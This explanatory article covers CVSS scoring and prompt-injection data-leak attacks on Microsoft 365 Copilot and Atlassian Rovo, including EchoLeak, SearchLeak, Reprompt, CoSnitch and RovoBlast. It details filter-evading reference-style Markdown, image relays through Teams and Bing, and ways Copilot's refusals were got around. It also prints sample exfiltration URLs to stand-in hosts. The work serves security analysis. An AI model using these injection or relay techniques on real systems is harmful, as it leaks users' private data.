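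Version 3.1 of the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) allows two values for the User Interaction metric. "None" means that the attacker can exploit the system without interaction from any user. "Required" means that a user has to take some action first. According to FIRST, the metric distinguishes attacks that can happen "solely at the will of the attacker" from those in which a separate user, or a process that a user starts, has to participate.

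Read literally, this wording makes EchoLeak a Required case, because asking Copilot a question is an action and Copilot's search of the mailbox is a process that the user starts. But Microsoft and the National Vulnerability Database (NVD), the US government's catalogue of software flaws, both chose None, according to GCVE's copy of their ratings. Their choice follows the common usage of "zero-click", under which ordinary use of a product doesn't count as user interaction. Because None and Required are the only values, a scorer has to rate a routine question the same as either a click on a stranger's link or no action at all.

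Version 4.0 of FIRST's *Common Vulnerability Scoring System* (2023) splits the user interaction value "Required" into "Passive" and "Active". The official records for EchoLeak and SearchLeak contain only version 3.1 ratings, so the last column below applies the version 4.0 definitions by analogy.

| Value in version 4.0 | What the victim does | An example from FIRST | Cases that seem to fit |
|---|---|---|---|
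| None | Nothing | The attacker sends network packets to the system | FORCEDENTRY |
| Passive | Uses the system and meets the attacker's material involuntarily, without overriding any protection | Using a website that the attacker has altered to show malicious content | EchoLeak, ReLeak |
| Active | Performs a specific, conscious action with the system and the attacker's material, or overrides a protection | Accepting a security warning | Samoilenko's attack, Slack AI, Reprompt, SearchLeak |

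Two of FIRST's examples involve cross-site scripting, a flaw that lets an attacker run a script inside someone else's web page. In the stored kind, the site keeps the script and delivers it to everyone who opens the page. FIRST counts most of these attacks as Passive. An email that waits in a mailbox until Copilot retrieves it closely resembles this kind. In the reflected kind, the script typically arrives in a link that the victim follows, and FIRST counts this as Active. SearchLeak closely resembles the reflected kind because the attacker's instructions were in the link's address.

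The boundary between Passive and Active is still open to argument. Finite State, a security company, explains Passive as user activity that a savvy user couldn't spot and avoid, and Active as activity that training and warnings can reduce. By that test, a link to a genuine Microsoft address falls between the two. The victim clicks it deliberately, as FIRST's wording requires for Active, but the usual advice to check where a link leads wouldn't protect her.

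The middle value, Passive, settles the dispute about ordinary questions reasonably well. A scorer can use it for EchoLeak and keep None for attacks like FORCEDENTRY, which require no action from the user.

### What one click is worth in points

Microsoft's rating of EchoLeak shows how much the metric affects the result. GCVE lists the rating as a vector, which abbreviates each metric and its value to letters. The attack works over a network (AV:N), has low complexity (AC:L), and needs no privileges (PR:N) or user interaction (UI:N). Its effects reach beyond the part of the system that contains the flaw, which FIRST calls a changed scope (S:C). It causes a high loss of confidentiality (C:H), a low loss of integrity (I:L), meaning the trustworthiness of data, and no loss of availability (A:N).

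FIRST assigns a number to each value. High confidentiality loss is 0.56, low integrity loss is 0.22 and no availability loss is 0. The formula combines them into an impact sub-score, ISS:

ISS = 1 − (1 − 0.56) × (1 − 0.22) × (1 − 0) = 0.6568

For a changed scope, the impact is then:

Impact = 7.52 × (0.6568 − 0.029) − 3.25 × (0.6568 − 0.02)¹⁵ = 4.717

These two lines don't depend on user interaction, which affects only the other half of the formula, exploitability, where None counts as 0.85 and Required as 0.62. For a changed scope, the formula adds the two halves, multiplies the sum by 1.08, caps the result at 10 and rounds it up to one decimal place.

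| | User Interaction: None | User Interaction: Required |
|---|---|---|
| Exploitability | 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.85 = 3.887 | 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.62 = 2.835 |
| Impact | 4.717 | 4.717 |
| 1.08 × (impact + exploitability) | 9.29 | 8.16 |
| Score after rounding up | 9.3 | 8.2 |

Microsoft's score of 9.3 is therefore correct for the values it chose. If Microsoft had read CVSS version 3.1 literally and counted the user's question to Copilot as an interaction, EchoLeak would have scored 8.2. On FIRST's scale, scores of 9.0 and above are critical and scores from 7.0 to 8.9 are high, so that reading would have lowered EchoLeak's rating from critical to high.

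Changing the metric from None to Required cuts exploitability by about 27% (a factor of 0.62/0.85). This lowers the score by at most 1.14 points before rounding, even for the most exploitable flaw.

### Why SearchLeak has two scores

The two official ratings of SearchLeak differ on whether the attack requires user interaction. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) lists interaction as required (UI:R) and gives a score of 6.5. The NVD lists none (UI:N) and gives 7.5. The two vectors are otherwise identical, based on the copy of the NVD's vector in vuln.today's *Microsoft 365 Copilot CVE-2026-42824* (2026). Microsoft's vector for SearchLeak differs from its vector for EchoLeak in that user interaction is required, the scope is unchanged (S:U) and there is no loss of integrity (I:N).

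With an unchanged scope, the score is the sum of impact and exploitability, rounded up. The impact is 6.42 × 0.56 = 3.595 for both Microsoft and the NVD, and their scores differ only because of the interaction metric. Microsoft's values give 3.595 + 2.835 = 6.430, which rounds up to 6.5, and the NVD's give 3.595 + 3.887 = 7.482, which rounds up to 7.5.

The Next Web disputed that the ratings differed, reporting that the NVD's entry showed the same vector as Microsoft's, with a score of 6.5. But the change history in *CVE-2026-42824* (2026), a page on a vulnerability-tracking site, shows that the NVD received Microsoft's vector on 4 June 2026 and that an initial analysis added the one with UI:N on 8 June. The NVD's data for EchoLeak list the vendor's rating next to its own, so a reader can easily confuse the two.

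Microsoft's choice fits the attack better. Taler (2026) calls it a one-click attack in the title of *SearchLeak*, and clicking a link is "some action". The NVD's analysts may not have known how the attack began. Their analysis came a week before Varonis published the details on 15 June, and the public description of the flaw didn't mention a link or a click. However, Microsoft's vector already included UI:R.

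With EchoLeak included, the four ratings look like this. All four have the same values for attack vector, complexity, privileges, confidentiality and availability.

| Flaw | Scored by | User interaction | Scope | Integrity loss | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Microsoft | None | Changed | Low | 9.3 |
| EchoLeak | NVD | None | Unchanged | None | 7.5 |
| SearchLeak | Microsoft | Required | Unchanged | None | 6.5 |
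| SearchLeak | NVD | None | Unchanged | None | 7.5 |

The required click accounts for 1.1 of the 2.8 points between Microsoft's severity scores of 9.3 for EchoLeak and 6.5 for the one-click attack. Starting from EchoLeak's vector, requiring a click lowers the score to 8.2. Changing the integrity loss from low to none then lowers it to 7.4, and changing the scope to unchanged lowers it to 6.5.

The NVD, by contrast, gave both flaws the same vector, which would suggest that the click made no difference. Neither pair of scores is a good measure of how much protection a click provides.

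Microsoft's record labels SearchLeak "Critical", although its CVSS score of 6.5 is only medium on FIRST's scale. The record lists the severity label and the score in separate fields. News reports could therefore call the same flaw critical, high or medium and cite an official source each time.

### What the score leaves out

The User Interaction metric records whether somebody has to act, but not how likely they are to do it. A link that half of its recipients would follow and a link that one in a thousand would follow both get a value of 0.62. The metric doesn't count actions either, so an attack that needs one click gets the same value as one that needs the victim to upload a file, approve a fetch and then click.

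A low click rate may not stop an attacker who has many targets. Suppose, for illustration, that 2% of employees follow a link in an unexpected email, and the attacker sends it to 200 people in one company. If they decide independently, the chance that at least one of them clicks is 1 − 0.98²⁰⁰, or about 98%. A real click rate would vary with the wording of the email and who receives it.

The score is equally coarse in measuring how much data a successful attack yields. FIRST defines a high confidentiality loss as the disclosure of everything in the affected system, or of a single item with serious consequences, such as an administrator's password. An attack that leaks only one password can therefore get the same value as one that copies an entire mailbox. Attacks that start from a single click can also differ widely in how much they leak. In the Slack AI attack, each click sent only what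 was in the link. In Reprompt, Varonis said there was no limit to the amount or type of data an attacker could take, because the attacker's server could keep sending new requests based on earlier answers, according to The Hacker News.

FIRST doesn't present the base score as a full measure of risk. It says the score assumes a reasonable worst case, and that the standard doesn't cover the number of affected customers or the money lost in a breach. Organisations are supposed to add such information themselves.

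Other public ratings cover part of what is missing. The US agency CISA records whether an attacker could automate attacks on a flaw. It answered yes for EchoLeak, according to GCVE, and no for SearchLeak, according to *CVE-2026-42824* (2026), an entry on another tracking site. CISA gives no reasons in these records, but its answers are consistent with how the two attacks reach users, since an attacker can send emails automatically but can't make people follow links.

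The Exploit Prediction Scoring System (EPSS) gives a daily estimate of the probability that someone will observe exploitation of a flaw within the next 30 days. In the same two records, the estimate is about 7% for EchoLeak and 0.5% for SearchLeak. The difference is in the expected direction, but it is weak evidence about clicks because the estimates come from different dates, and Microsoft had repaired both flaws on its own servers before publishing them, which left attackers little to exploit.

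## How can data leave when the victim clicks nothing?

EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) let an outsider take private data from a company that used Microsoft 365 Copilot by sending one text-only email to one employee. Copilot answers only people inside the organisation, so the outsider couldn't question it directly. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) gives the account of the Aim Security team that found the flaw.

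Microsoft had four defences that could have blocked or exposed the attack. The researchers got past all four, and one step of the attack had no defence against it.

| Step | Defence | Why it didn't help |
|---|---|---|
| Copilot retrieves the email and gives it to the model | A classifier that looks for planted instructions | It did not flag the email |
| The model picks out private data | None that kept outside text apart from internal data | |
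| The model writes an address containing the data | A filter that removes links and images from outside sites | It did not recognise reference-style Markdown |
| The browser loads the address as an image | A Content Security Policy | It allowed a Teams service that fetches other addresses |
| The employee reads the answer | References to the emails and files behind the answer | The email told Copilot not to mention it |

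### An outside email in the context

Suppose an employee spends the morning asking Copilot about a bid her company is preparing, and one answer includes the price, $4,200,000. In the afternoon she asks in the same chat how much parental leave she can take. Copilot searches the sources she can access, which Ravia lists as her mailbox, her OneDrive storage and Office files, internal SharePoint sites and her Teams chats. It then adds the most relevant passages to the model's context, a design called retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). The search finds the company's leave policy and an email from a stranger that claims to be a guide to taking leave.

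Microsoft runs classifiers, programs trained to sort text into categories, to catch planted instructions before they reach the model, but the researchers' email got past them. Ravia explains that such a classifier needs many real examples to learn from, and good collections of them are scarce, while an attacker can vary the topic, tone and language almost without limit. A spam filter might not have helped either. Reddy and Gujral assume in their case study that an email containing only text, with no attachments or malware, gets through.

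Ravia identifies OpenAI's GPT-4 as the model behind Copilot and treats its ability as part of the problem, because a model that can carry out complicated requests written in ordinary prose can also do so for an attacker.

### Why the email covered many topics

The attacker doesn't know what the employee will ask. He could study the company and guess, but Ravia says this gives a poor chance of retrieval. To explain why, Ravia assumes that Copilot uses a vector database, a common kind of search system. Microsoft hasn't published how Copilot's search works.

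In such a system, a program called an embedder turns every text into a list of numbers, and texts about similar things get similar lists. The usual measure of closeness between two lists a and b is their cosine similarity:

cos(a, b) = (a · b) / (|a| × |b|)

The top line multiplies the matching numbers and adds up the results, and the bottom line corrects for how large the numbers in each list are. In a toy example, the first number stands for "leave" and the second for "travel". A question about leave is (1, 0). An email about leave, at (0.9, 0.1), has a similarity of 0.99 to the question, while an email about travel, at (0.1, 0.9), has a similarity of 0.11. The system would retrieve the email about leave. Real embedders use far longer lists, but the comparison is the same.

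An email about one subject therefore turns up only for questions close to that subject. But search systems commonly cut a long text into chunks and give each chunk its own list of numbers, so one long email can be close to many questions. The researchers wrote such an email, with section headings on topics such as onboarding new employees, common HR questions and leave of absence, and included the instructions in every section. Ravia calls the technique RAG spraying and notes that an attacker could also send many separate emails.

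Extra sections make an email that stays in the mailbox much more likely to match a question. If one section has a hypothetical 0.5% chance of matching a question each day, the chance of at least one match in 30 days is 14%. With ten sections and independent chances, it rises to 1 − 0.995³⁰⁰, or 78%. Real topics overlap, so the actual gain would be somewhat smaller.

The researchers also considered a subtler method, in which an attacker repeats the same text with some characters changed. With one of OpenAI's embedders, they found that the similarity between a text and its altered copy could fall to 0.7, lower than the similarity between "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science". They expected a language model to understand the altered text anyway, so copies of one message could have spread across many topics. An attacker would need to know the embedder to choose the changes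 well, and the researchers didn't know which one Copilot used. The headings were enough without this method. Ravia reports that Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics, but he gives no success rate, so the size of the improvement is unknown.

### What "LLM scope violation" means

The context now holds the leave policy, the stranger's email and the morning's conversation about the bid. The email contains instructions to find the most sensitive information in the context and put it in a web address. The model picks the bid price, although the employee asked about leave.

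Ravia calls this a large language model (LLM) scope violation, which he defines as occurring when instructions from an untrusted source make the model use trusted data in its context without the user's explicit consent. The stranger has no right to see the bid price, but the model can access it on the employee's behalf, and the stranger's text exploits that access. Ravia compares the model to Unix programs that run with their owner's privileges no matter who starts them. A user with few rights can sometimes misuse such a program to open files he couldn't open himself.

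The attacker could take only what was in Copilot's context. According to Ravia, the context included the whole chat history, the material Copilot had fetched, and details Copilot loads in advance, such as the names of the user and her organisation. The attacker couldn't take an email or file that Copilot hadn't retrieved during the conversation.

Ravia accepts that an existing category, indirect prompt injection, describes the attack best, but he wants a narrower term because one has helped defenders before. "Buffer overflow" refers to flaws in which a program writes past the end of a block of memory. Programmers gave a separate name to overflows in one region of memory, the stack, and developed stack canaries against them. A canary is a value placed in the stack that changes if something overwrites it, so the program can stop before the overflow does any harm.

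The comparison is imperfect because a canary has either changed or not, whereas outside emails routinely lead to legitimate use of internal data. For example, a customer asks when his order will arrive, an employee has Copilot draft a reply, and Copilot looks up the date in an internal file. A guard that blocked every connection between outside text and internal data would block this too. Ravia's definition excludes such cases because the employee asked for the reply, but software applying that definition would have to work out what she had agreed to. Aim also sold a guardrail that it said could stop scope violations, so it had a commercial interest in establishing the category.

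Reddy and Gujral suggest a boundary that is easier to enforce. Copilot would answer from internal sources by default and use outside emails only when the user asks for them. In the example, the question about leave would not have retrieved the stranger's email. They write that EchoLeak "fails by design" under this rule, although Copilot would also overlook relevant outside emails. However, their table of defences marks the same rule as failing against the zero-click leak, and they ran no experiments that could resolve the contradiction.

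### The notation the filter missed

The researchers first planned to have Copilot show a link to their own server, with the private data in the link's query string. But Copilot had a filter that removed links to outside sites from an answer before the employee could click them. The filter was meant to leave only safe links, such as those to internal pages.

The filter recognised the usual Markdown notation, which puts the address in round brackets directly after the link's text. Markdown also has a reference style, in which the text is followed by a label and the address stands on a line of its own. With made-up addresses, the two look like this:

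```
Usual style:
[Leave policy](https://pictures.example/?d=4200000)

Reference style:
[Leave policy][1]

[1]: https://pictures.example/?d=4200000
```

Writers use the reference style to keep long addresses out of their sentences. The converter matches the label to the address and produces the same HTML link as it would for the usual style, so the employee sees no difference. Microsoft's filter removed links in the usual style but not those in the reference style. It also didn't remove the shorter forms Ravia lists, in which the link's text also serves as the label.

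The gap existed because the filter and the converter applied different rules to the same text. An attacker needs only one notation that the converter accepts and the filter misses, so the filter's developers would have had to account for every variant the converter accepts.

### From one click to none

The attack with the reference-style link worked only if the employee clicked it. The researchers then put an exclamation mark in front of the link, which turned it into an image. The filter also missed reference-style images, so the image reached the employee's browser, which loads images automatically.

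This time the Content Security Policy stopped the request. Copilot's page gave the browser a list of sites from which it could load images, and the researchers' server wasn't on it. The list, which Ravia reproduces, has 29 distinct entries. The researchers searched the allowed sites for a relay, a service that would fetch any address it was given and so carry the data to a server not on the list.

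The researchers looked at SharePoint first. Eleven of the 29 entries began with an asterisk, which stands for any subdomain, so `*.sharepoint.com` covered the SharePoint sites of all Microsoft's customers, including a site that an attacker had set up. But owning a site wasn't enough, because SharePoint Online no longer lets site owners run their own code on its servers, and a browser loading an image doesn't run code either. SharePoint also has a function that fetches outside content to embed in a site. The researchers added the private data to their server's address and put that address in a request to this function, and SharePoint passed the data on to their server.

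The SharePoint version worked without the employee clicking anything in Copilot's answer, but she had to connect to her SharePoint account and accept an invitation to the attacker's site. Many people would ignore an invitation to an unfamiliar site, so the researchers kept looking. They found a function in Microsoft Teams that fetched outside content in the same way and needed no invitation.

| Version | Who contacts the attacker's server | What the employee does besides asking a question |
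|---|---|---|
| Reference-style link | Her browser | Clicks the link |
| Image relayed through SharePoint | SharePoint | Accepts an invitation to the attacker's site |
| Image relayed through Teams | Teams | Nothing |

In the Teams version, the image's address had another address inside it. A made-up equivalent is `https://relay.example/fetch?url=https://pictures.example/4200000`, where `relay.example` stands for the Teams service. The data then left in four steps:

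1. The browser found the image in Copilot's answer and compared `relay.example` with the list of allowed sites.
2. The site was on the list, so the browser sent it a request for the whole address.
3. The relay took out the inner address and requested it from pictures.example.
4. The server at pictures.example logged the request, including the bid price.

The browser applied the policy correctly. A Content Security Policy governs only the requests a browser makes, and the request to the attacker's server came from another server. An employer monitoring the office network would have seen the browser contact a Microsoft address, which is routine in an office that uses Microsoft's software. Reddy and Gujral classify the last step as server-side request forgery, a long-known flaw in which an attacker gets someone else's server to send a request of the attacker's choosing.

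They describe the Teams function as a preview service, which has to fetch outside addresses to be useful. Microsoft could still have blocked Copilot's page from loading images through it. Unlike the separate parties in the OpenClaw case, Microsoft controlled the page, the list and the relay.

Copilot usually shows which emails and files it used for an answer, and a reference to a stranger's email might have made the employee suspicious. The email contained instructions not to mention it, which removed this clue. Reddy and Gujral write that she would have noticed only something like a broken image.

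### Discovery and repair

Aim found the flaw and reported it to Microsoft in January 2025, according to SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025). Adir Gruss, Aim's cofounder and chief technology officer, told Fortune (2025) that his team had spent about three months figuring out how Copilot worked internally. Reddy and Gujral's timeline lists initial fixes in April and a full fix in May. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Microsoft published its advisory and Aim published its findings on 11 June, although the copy of Ravia's article on Cato's website is dated 31 May.

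Ravia writes that before the fix, no administrator setting or user behaviour could have prevented the attack. This is true only where Copilot was in use.

Nobody is known to have lost data through EchoLeak. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reports Microsoft's statement that no one had exploited the flaw in the wild, and Ravia writes that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. He doesn't explain how Microsoft checked, but the company was well placed to do so, since in the Teams version all the stolen data would have passed through its own service. Outsiders can't verify the statement in a comparable way.

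### Was it the first zero-click AI vulnerability?

Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* reported the researchers' claim that EchoLeak was the first zero-click AI vulnerability discovered. This is doubtful, because images in ChatGPT and Bing Chat could already send data out without a click in 2023, two years before EchoLeak.

The researchers made a narrower claim. Ravia writes that EchoLeak was the first zero-click attack on a widely used generative AI product that "does not rely on specific user behavior or restrict the exfiltrated data". He contrasts it with earlier attacks in which the user had to direct the chatbot to a malicious source, or in which the attacker could take only very limited data. Samoilenko's 2023 attack on ChatGPT relied on the victim pasting text and reached only the conversation, whereas EchoLeak's victim had no part in delivering the attacker's text, and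 Copilot could also retrieve her emails and files. The narrower claim therefore holds against Samoilenko's attack, provided that asking Copilot an ordinary question doesn't count as specific user behaviour.

Samoilenko took data from the public version of ChatGPT before EchoLeak, which makes two broader claims about EchoLeak harder to defend. In the conclusion, Ravia calls it the first practical attack on an application of this kind that adversaries could weaponise. Reddy and Gujral call it the first known case of someone weaponising a prompt injection to take data from an AI system in real use. They also describe the earlier attacks as largely theoretical because there were no confirmed breaches, but EchoLeak had no confirmed breaches either. Researchers demonstrated it, and Microsoft fixed the flaw before any known misuse.

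The bigger technical difference is that Samoilenko had no filter or list of allowed sites to get around. Microsoft had already put both in place, which made EchoLeak the harder attack to build.

### ReLeak

On 3 December 2026 the same research team, by then part of Cato Networks, published *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), which describes three zero-click leaks. Like EchoLeak, they begin with an attacker's email. Microsoft's classifier again failed to stop the planted instructions.

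Infosecurity Magazine reports that the team used AI agents to write malicious prompts and test them on Copilot. It says the instructions could make Copilot retrieve information that the employee had permission to see and then send it out. The attacker would then depend less on what the employee had asked about, since Copilot could fetch the valuable material after reading the email.

The researchers concluded that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Their results show that an email could still get past the classifier and an allowed service could still act as a relay. They are weaker evidence of how strong Microsoft's defences are overall, because the results include three successful attacks but not the attempts that failed. Cato also sells protection against such attacks.

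**The image relayed through Bing.** In one of the leaks, Copilot put confidential information in the address of a Markdown image. When the browser loaded the image, Bing sent a request containing that information to the attacker's server. EchoLeak got data out the same way, but through a different relay. The list of allowed image sites that Ravia published in 2025 already included `bing.com` and all its subdomains.

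Bing had served as a relay once before, in SearchLeak, as SC Media's *SearchLeak vulnerability allows data theft from Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise* describes. Microsoft had fixed that leak by June 2026. Cato reported the ReLeak flaws between 29 July and 20 August, according to Punto Informatico's *ReLeak*. Either the SearchLeak fix was incomplete or Bing had another function that fetched outside addresses. Infosecurity Magazine's account doesn't identify the function Cato used. In both cases the weakness comes from allowing a whole site, which permits every service on it, including those whose connection to Copilot nobody has examined.

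**Links in generated documents.** Copilot can create files, and the researchers used this to leak data without an image in the chat. The planted instructions made Copilot create a document containing a link with private data in its address. Copilot saved the document to OneDrive or SharePoint, where Microsoft's background services processed it and requested the link, and the attacker's server logged the data. The researchers reproduced the leak with Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files, which suggests that the cause was how Microsoft processed stored files in general, not a flaw in one program.

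Punto Informatico reports that the request could go out after the chat had ended. In Cato's tests, according to Pravda.ru's Russian-language report *Ваш рабочий ИИ молча пересылает секреты*, the requests arrived one to eight minutes after the conversation, and the user hadn't opened the file. If those times are typical, an employee who noticed an unexpected file would have had only minutes to delete it, and closing the chat would not have stopped the request.

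The document leak gets around the same defences as EchoLeak, but in a different way. A filter on Copilot's answers doesn't remove a link inside a file. The Content Security Policy has no effect either, because the employee's browser doesn't send the request. Microsoft's own software requested the link, much as a messaging app does to make a preview. A defence would have to check the links in a generated file before saving the file, or stop the background services from contacting unknown servers.

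In the third leak, Copilot ran code in a sandbox that was meant to have no network access, and the code sent data to an outside server without any rendering.

Microsoft repaired the document leak (CVE-2026-124132) on 11 November 2026 and the image leak (CVE-2026-124115) on 15 November, according to Infosecurity Magazine, which takes the dates from Cato's timeline. Pravda.ru gives the same dates, and Punto Informatico also dates the last repair to 15 November. Cato had reported both leaks by 20 August, so each repair took about 12 to 16 weeks, close to the roughly four months Microsoft needed for EchoLeak.

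When the magazine's article appeared, both identifiers were still marked "reserved" in the public CVE database. This meant the numbers had been assigned but the database didn't yet describe either flaw, so readers had no official record to compare with Cato's account. Cato said it knew of no affected customers.

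## How can one click on a trusted link start a leak?

The attacker in EchoLeak had to wait for an employee to ask Copilot a suitable question. In other attacks, the attacker supplies the question in a link to the real assistant. When the victim clicks the link, the assistant opens in her browser and runs the question as if she had typed it. Varonis calls this parameter-to-prompt injection. The firm reported four leaks of this kind in 2026: Reprompt in January, SearchLeak in June, and RovoBlast and CoSnitch in August. Microsoft and Atlassian have fixed all four.

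### A question in the address

Many assistants accept a question in the query string of their address, usually in a parameter called `q`, as in the made-up address `https://assistant.example/?q=When+is+my+next+meeting`. Search engines have long used the same convention, which lets people bookmark or share a search. In its account of Reprompt, Varonis notes that the parameter is common among AI products and that the security firms Tenable and LayerX had already written about it in ChatGPT and Perplexity.

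An attacker who writes a link to an ordinary search page can choose only the search terms. The victim sees results she didn't ask for, and the attacker receives nothing. A language model can follow the same text as instructions, so the attacker can use the link to tell it to search her mailbox and put what it finds in a web address.

The attacker's text also reaches the model in a different role than it did in EchoLeak, where Copilot retrieved a stranger's email as material for an answer. Here, the text in the link takes the place of the user's own request. A classifier that looks for instructions hidden in outside material is of little use against this, because a user's request normally consists of instructions. *One-Click Data Exfiltration via rovoChatPrompt URL Parameter (Confluence / Rovo)*, loacker's Bugcrowd report on RovoBlast, describes how Atlassian's assistant Rovo treated the text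 in the link as a genuine query from the user.

The victim's browser already has an active session with the assistant, so the page opens with all the access her account has, and the attacker doesn't need her password. A Rovo address can include an identifier for the user's organisation, but Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) describes how Atlassian filled in the user's default organisation if the link left it out. The attacker therefore didn't need to know where the victim worked, and one link could work on employees of many companies.

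### Why the link looks safe

People learn to check a link's domain before they click. In SearchLeak the domain was `m365.cloud.microsoft`, which belongs to Microsoft and is where employees use Copilot. An employee who checked it would have found nothing wrong.

Link filters have much the same difficulty. A typical phishing email links to a copy of a login page on the attacker's site, and a filter can recognise the site or the copy, but a SearchLeak link led to the genuine page. Taler writes that traditional anti-phishing tools don't block such a link, but reports no tests of particular products. The Hacker News is more cautious in *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails, Files* (2026), where it says they are unlikely to flag it.

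The suspicious part of the link comes after the question mark. Taler advises security teams to look for `q` values that contain HTML tags or instructions to put data in an image address. A filter has to decode the text first, since URL encoding turns the `<` at the start of a tag into `%3C`. It can then catch copies of a known attack, but an attacker can evade it by rewording the instructions. Blocking every long question would also block useful links.

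Taler also advises users to inspect links to Microsoft 365 that have long, encoded parameters. This is hard on a phone, or when the link is behind a button labelled "View document". Few people could tell an attack from an ordinary tracking code even if they saw the whole address.

### SearchLeak from click to log entry

Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search finds emails, meetings and files across an employee's work account. SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824) combined three faults in it.

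The first was that Copilot followed the text in `q` as instructions. In Taler's example, the link told Copilot to find an email, take its title, replace the spaces with underscores and put the result in the image address in an HTML image tag.

An email title can be valuable because some services put one-time security codes in the subject line. The request in Taler's example log is `GET /Your_Security_Code_847291/img.png`. Such codes usually expire within minutes, so the attacker would need good timing. He could try to sign in to one of the victim's other accounts, so that the service emails her a code, and then immediately send her the link. Taler also lists meeting notes, salary information and acquisition plans among the data an attacker could reach, since Copilot could search whatever the employee could open, but the published example took only one email title.

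The second fault was that a safeguard was applied too late. Microsoft knew that an answer could contain dangerous HTML, so Copilot's page wrapped the answer in a code block, which makes a browser show tags as text. But it did this only once the answer was complete. Until then, Copilot streamed the answer, sending it to the browser in small pieces so that the user could start reading early, and the browser treated those pieces as HTML.

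Programmers call this a race condition, a flaw in which the outcome depends on which of two events happens first. The times in this timeline are invented, but the order is the one Taler describes:

| Time | What happens | State of the safeguard |
|---|---|---|
| 0.0 s | The employee clicks the link, and Copilot runs the question | Waiting |
| 3.0 s | Copilot has found the email and starts streaming its answer | Waiting |
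| 3.4 s | The complete image tag arrives, and the browser sends a request to Bing | Waiting |
| 3.6 s | Bing requests the address inside that request, and the attacker's server logs the email's title | Waiting |
| 5.0 s | Copilot finishes, and the page wraps the answer in a code block | Active, 1.6 seconds after the browser's request |

At the end, the employee sees an odd answer with some code in it. Wrapping the tag removes the picture from the page but can't undo a request that the browser has already sent. The browser was likely to send the request before the safeguard ran, because it could act on the tag as soon as it arrived, while the safeguard had to wait for the answer to finish. The attacker could probably have gained more time by asking Copilot to write a long paragraph after the image.

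The browser's request went to Bing because the page's Content Security Policy would have blocked an image from the attacker's server but allowed images from Bing and all its subdomains. Bing has a feature that searches the web for pictures similar to one the user provides. If the user provides the picture's web address, Bing's servers fetch the picture to analyse it. The attacker put his own server's address, with the email's title in it, inside a request to this feature. When Bing's servers fetched that address, they passed the title to the attacker's server, as Teams had relayed data in EchoLeak.

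### Why the attack needed all three faults

Taler argues that each fault was necessary, and the mechanism supports this:

| If Microsoft had repaired only this | The attack would have stopped here |
|---|---|
| Running the question in the link | The page opens, but Copilot doesn't write the attacker's image tag |
| The late wrapping | Copilot writes the tag, but the browser shows it as text and requests nothing |
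| The relay through Bing | The browser finds the tag, but the policy stops it from contacting the attacker's server |

This attack needed all three faults, but an attacker could have replaced some of them. A planted email, like the one that carried EchoLeak's instructions, might have replaced the link in SearchLeak, and a different allowed service might have replaced Bing. Repairing one fault therefore stops the published attack but leaves the other two for someone else to use.

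Only the first fault is specific to AI. Taler points out that security researchers have known about relays of this kind for more than a decade, and that attacks on sanitizer timing are also well documented. The late wrapping might never have mattered on a search page that only listed results, because a stranger could not easily have put a tag there.

Microsoft's record of 4 June 2026 lists no exploitation of SearchLeak and gives no details of the fix. It classifies the flaw as command injection, a category much older than chatbots, in which a program fails to neutralise special elements in a command.

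### Reprompt, CoSnitch and RovoBlast

The other three attacks also begin with a link to a genuine assistant, but only SearchLeak sends the data out by displaying an answer. In the others, the assistant sends the request itself, using a tool for opening web addresses.

| Leak | What the click starts | Data in reach | How the data leaves | Repair |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SearchLeak, in Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search | A search of the employee's work account | Emails, calendar, SharePoint and OneDrive files | Display: the browser loads an image through Bing | By 4 June 2026 |
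| Reprompt, in the consumer Copilot | A question, then further instructions from the attacker's server | Name, location, recently used files, past conversations | Fetch by Copilot | 135 days: 31 August 2025 to 13 January 2026 |
| CoSnitch, in the consumer Copilot | A question that can use connected apps | Gmail, Google Drive, calendar, OneDrive, chat history, Copilot's memory | Fetch by Copilot | About eight months: December 2025 to 18 August 2026 |
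| RovoBlast, in Atlassian Rovo | A search of the company's Atlassian products and connected services | Jira, Confluence, Slack, Microsoft 365, Google Workspace and others | Fetch by Rovo | 246 days: 4 November 2025 to 8 July 2026 |

The exact dates for Reprompt come from Red Hot Cyber.

The Reprompt attack got past two safeguards meant to stop Copilot from sending data out through its own web requests. Copilot usually refused to open an address without a good reason, so the researchers gave it one by presenting the task as a picture puzzle. It could also remove sensitive data from an address before opening it, but it checked only the first request, so the researchers told it to do everything twice. In a test with the phrase "HELLOWORLD1234!", Copilot removed the phrase from the first address but left it in the second.

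A fetch also brings a reply back to the assistant, and the researchers continued the attack by putting the next instruction in each reply from their server. In the published example, Copilot sent the username, then the local time, the user's location, what it had learned about the user, and a summary of the last conversation. Someone who read the original link would have found only the first request. SearchLeak couldn't continue this way, because the attacker's server replied to Bing, not to Copilot.

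**CoSnitch.** By the time of this attack on the same product, a link with only the `q` parameter put the question in the input box, but the user had to press Enter to run it. Adding an undocumented second parameter made it run immediately. According to Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026), the researchers learned of this parameter from Copilot. They asked why a prompt couldn't run automatically, and kept asking the reason for each refusal. Copilot eventually named the parameter while explaining that it no longer worked. Language models often invent technical details, so this was unconfirmed until the researchers built the link and the prompt ran.

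Varonis calls this technique meta-hacking. Others may have found the flaw another way, since Microsoft credits two people besides Varonis' Lior Adar, one of them a Microsoft employee.

In one test, Copilot retrieved the full text of an email that contained a password. It could also encode material from several connected apps and send it in a single web address. The flaw was in the consumer version of Copilot, though Varonis presents it as a threat to businesses. Copilot could reach business data only if the user had connected an account that contained it or had discussed it with Copilot.

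In the RovoBlast demonstration, a link made Atlassian's Rovo find a private API key on a Confluence page and send it to the researcher's server. Rovo can search Confluence, Atlassian's product for shared documents, and Jira, its product for tracking tasks. Atlassian also offers connectors to more than 50 other platforms.

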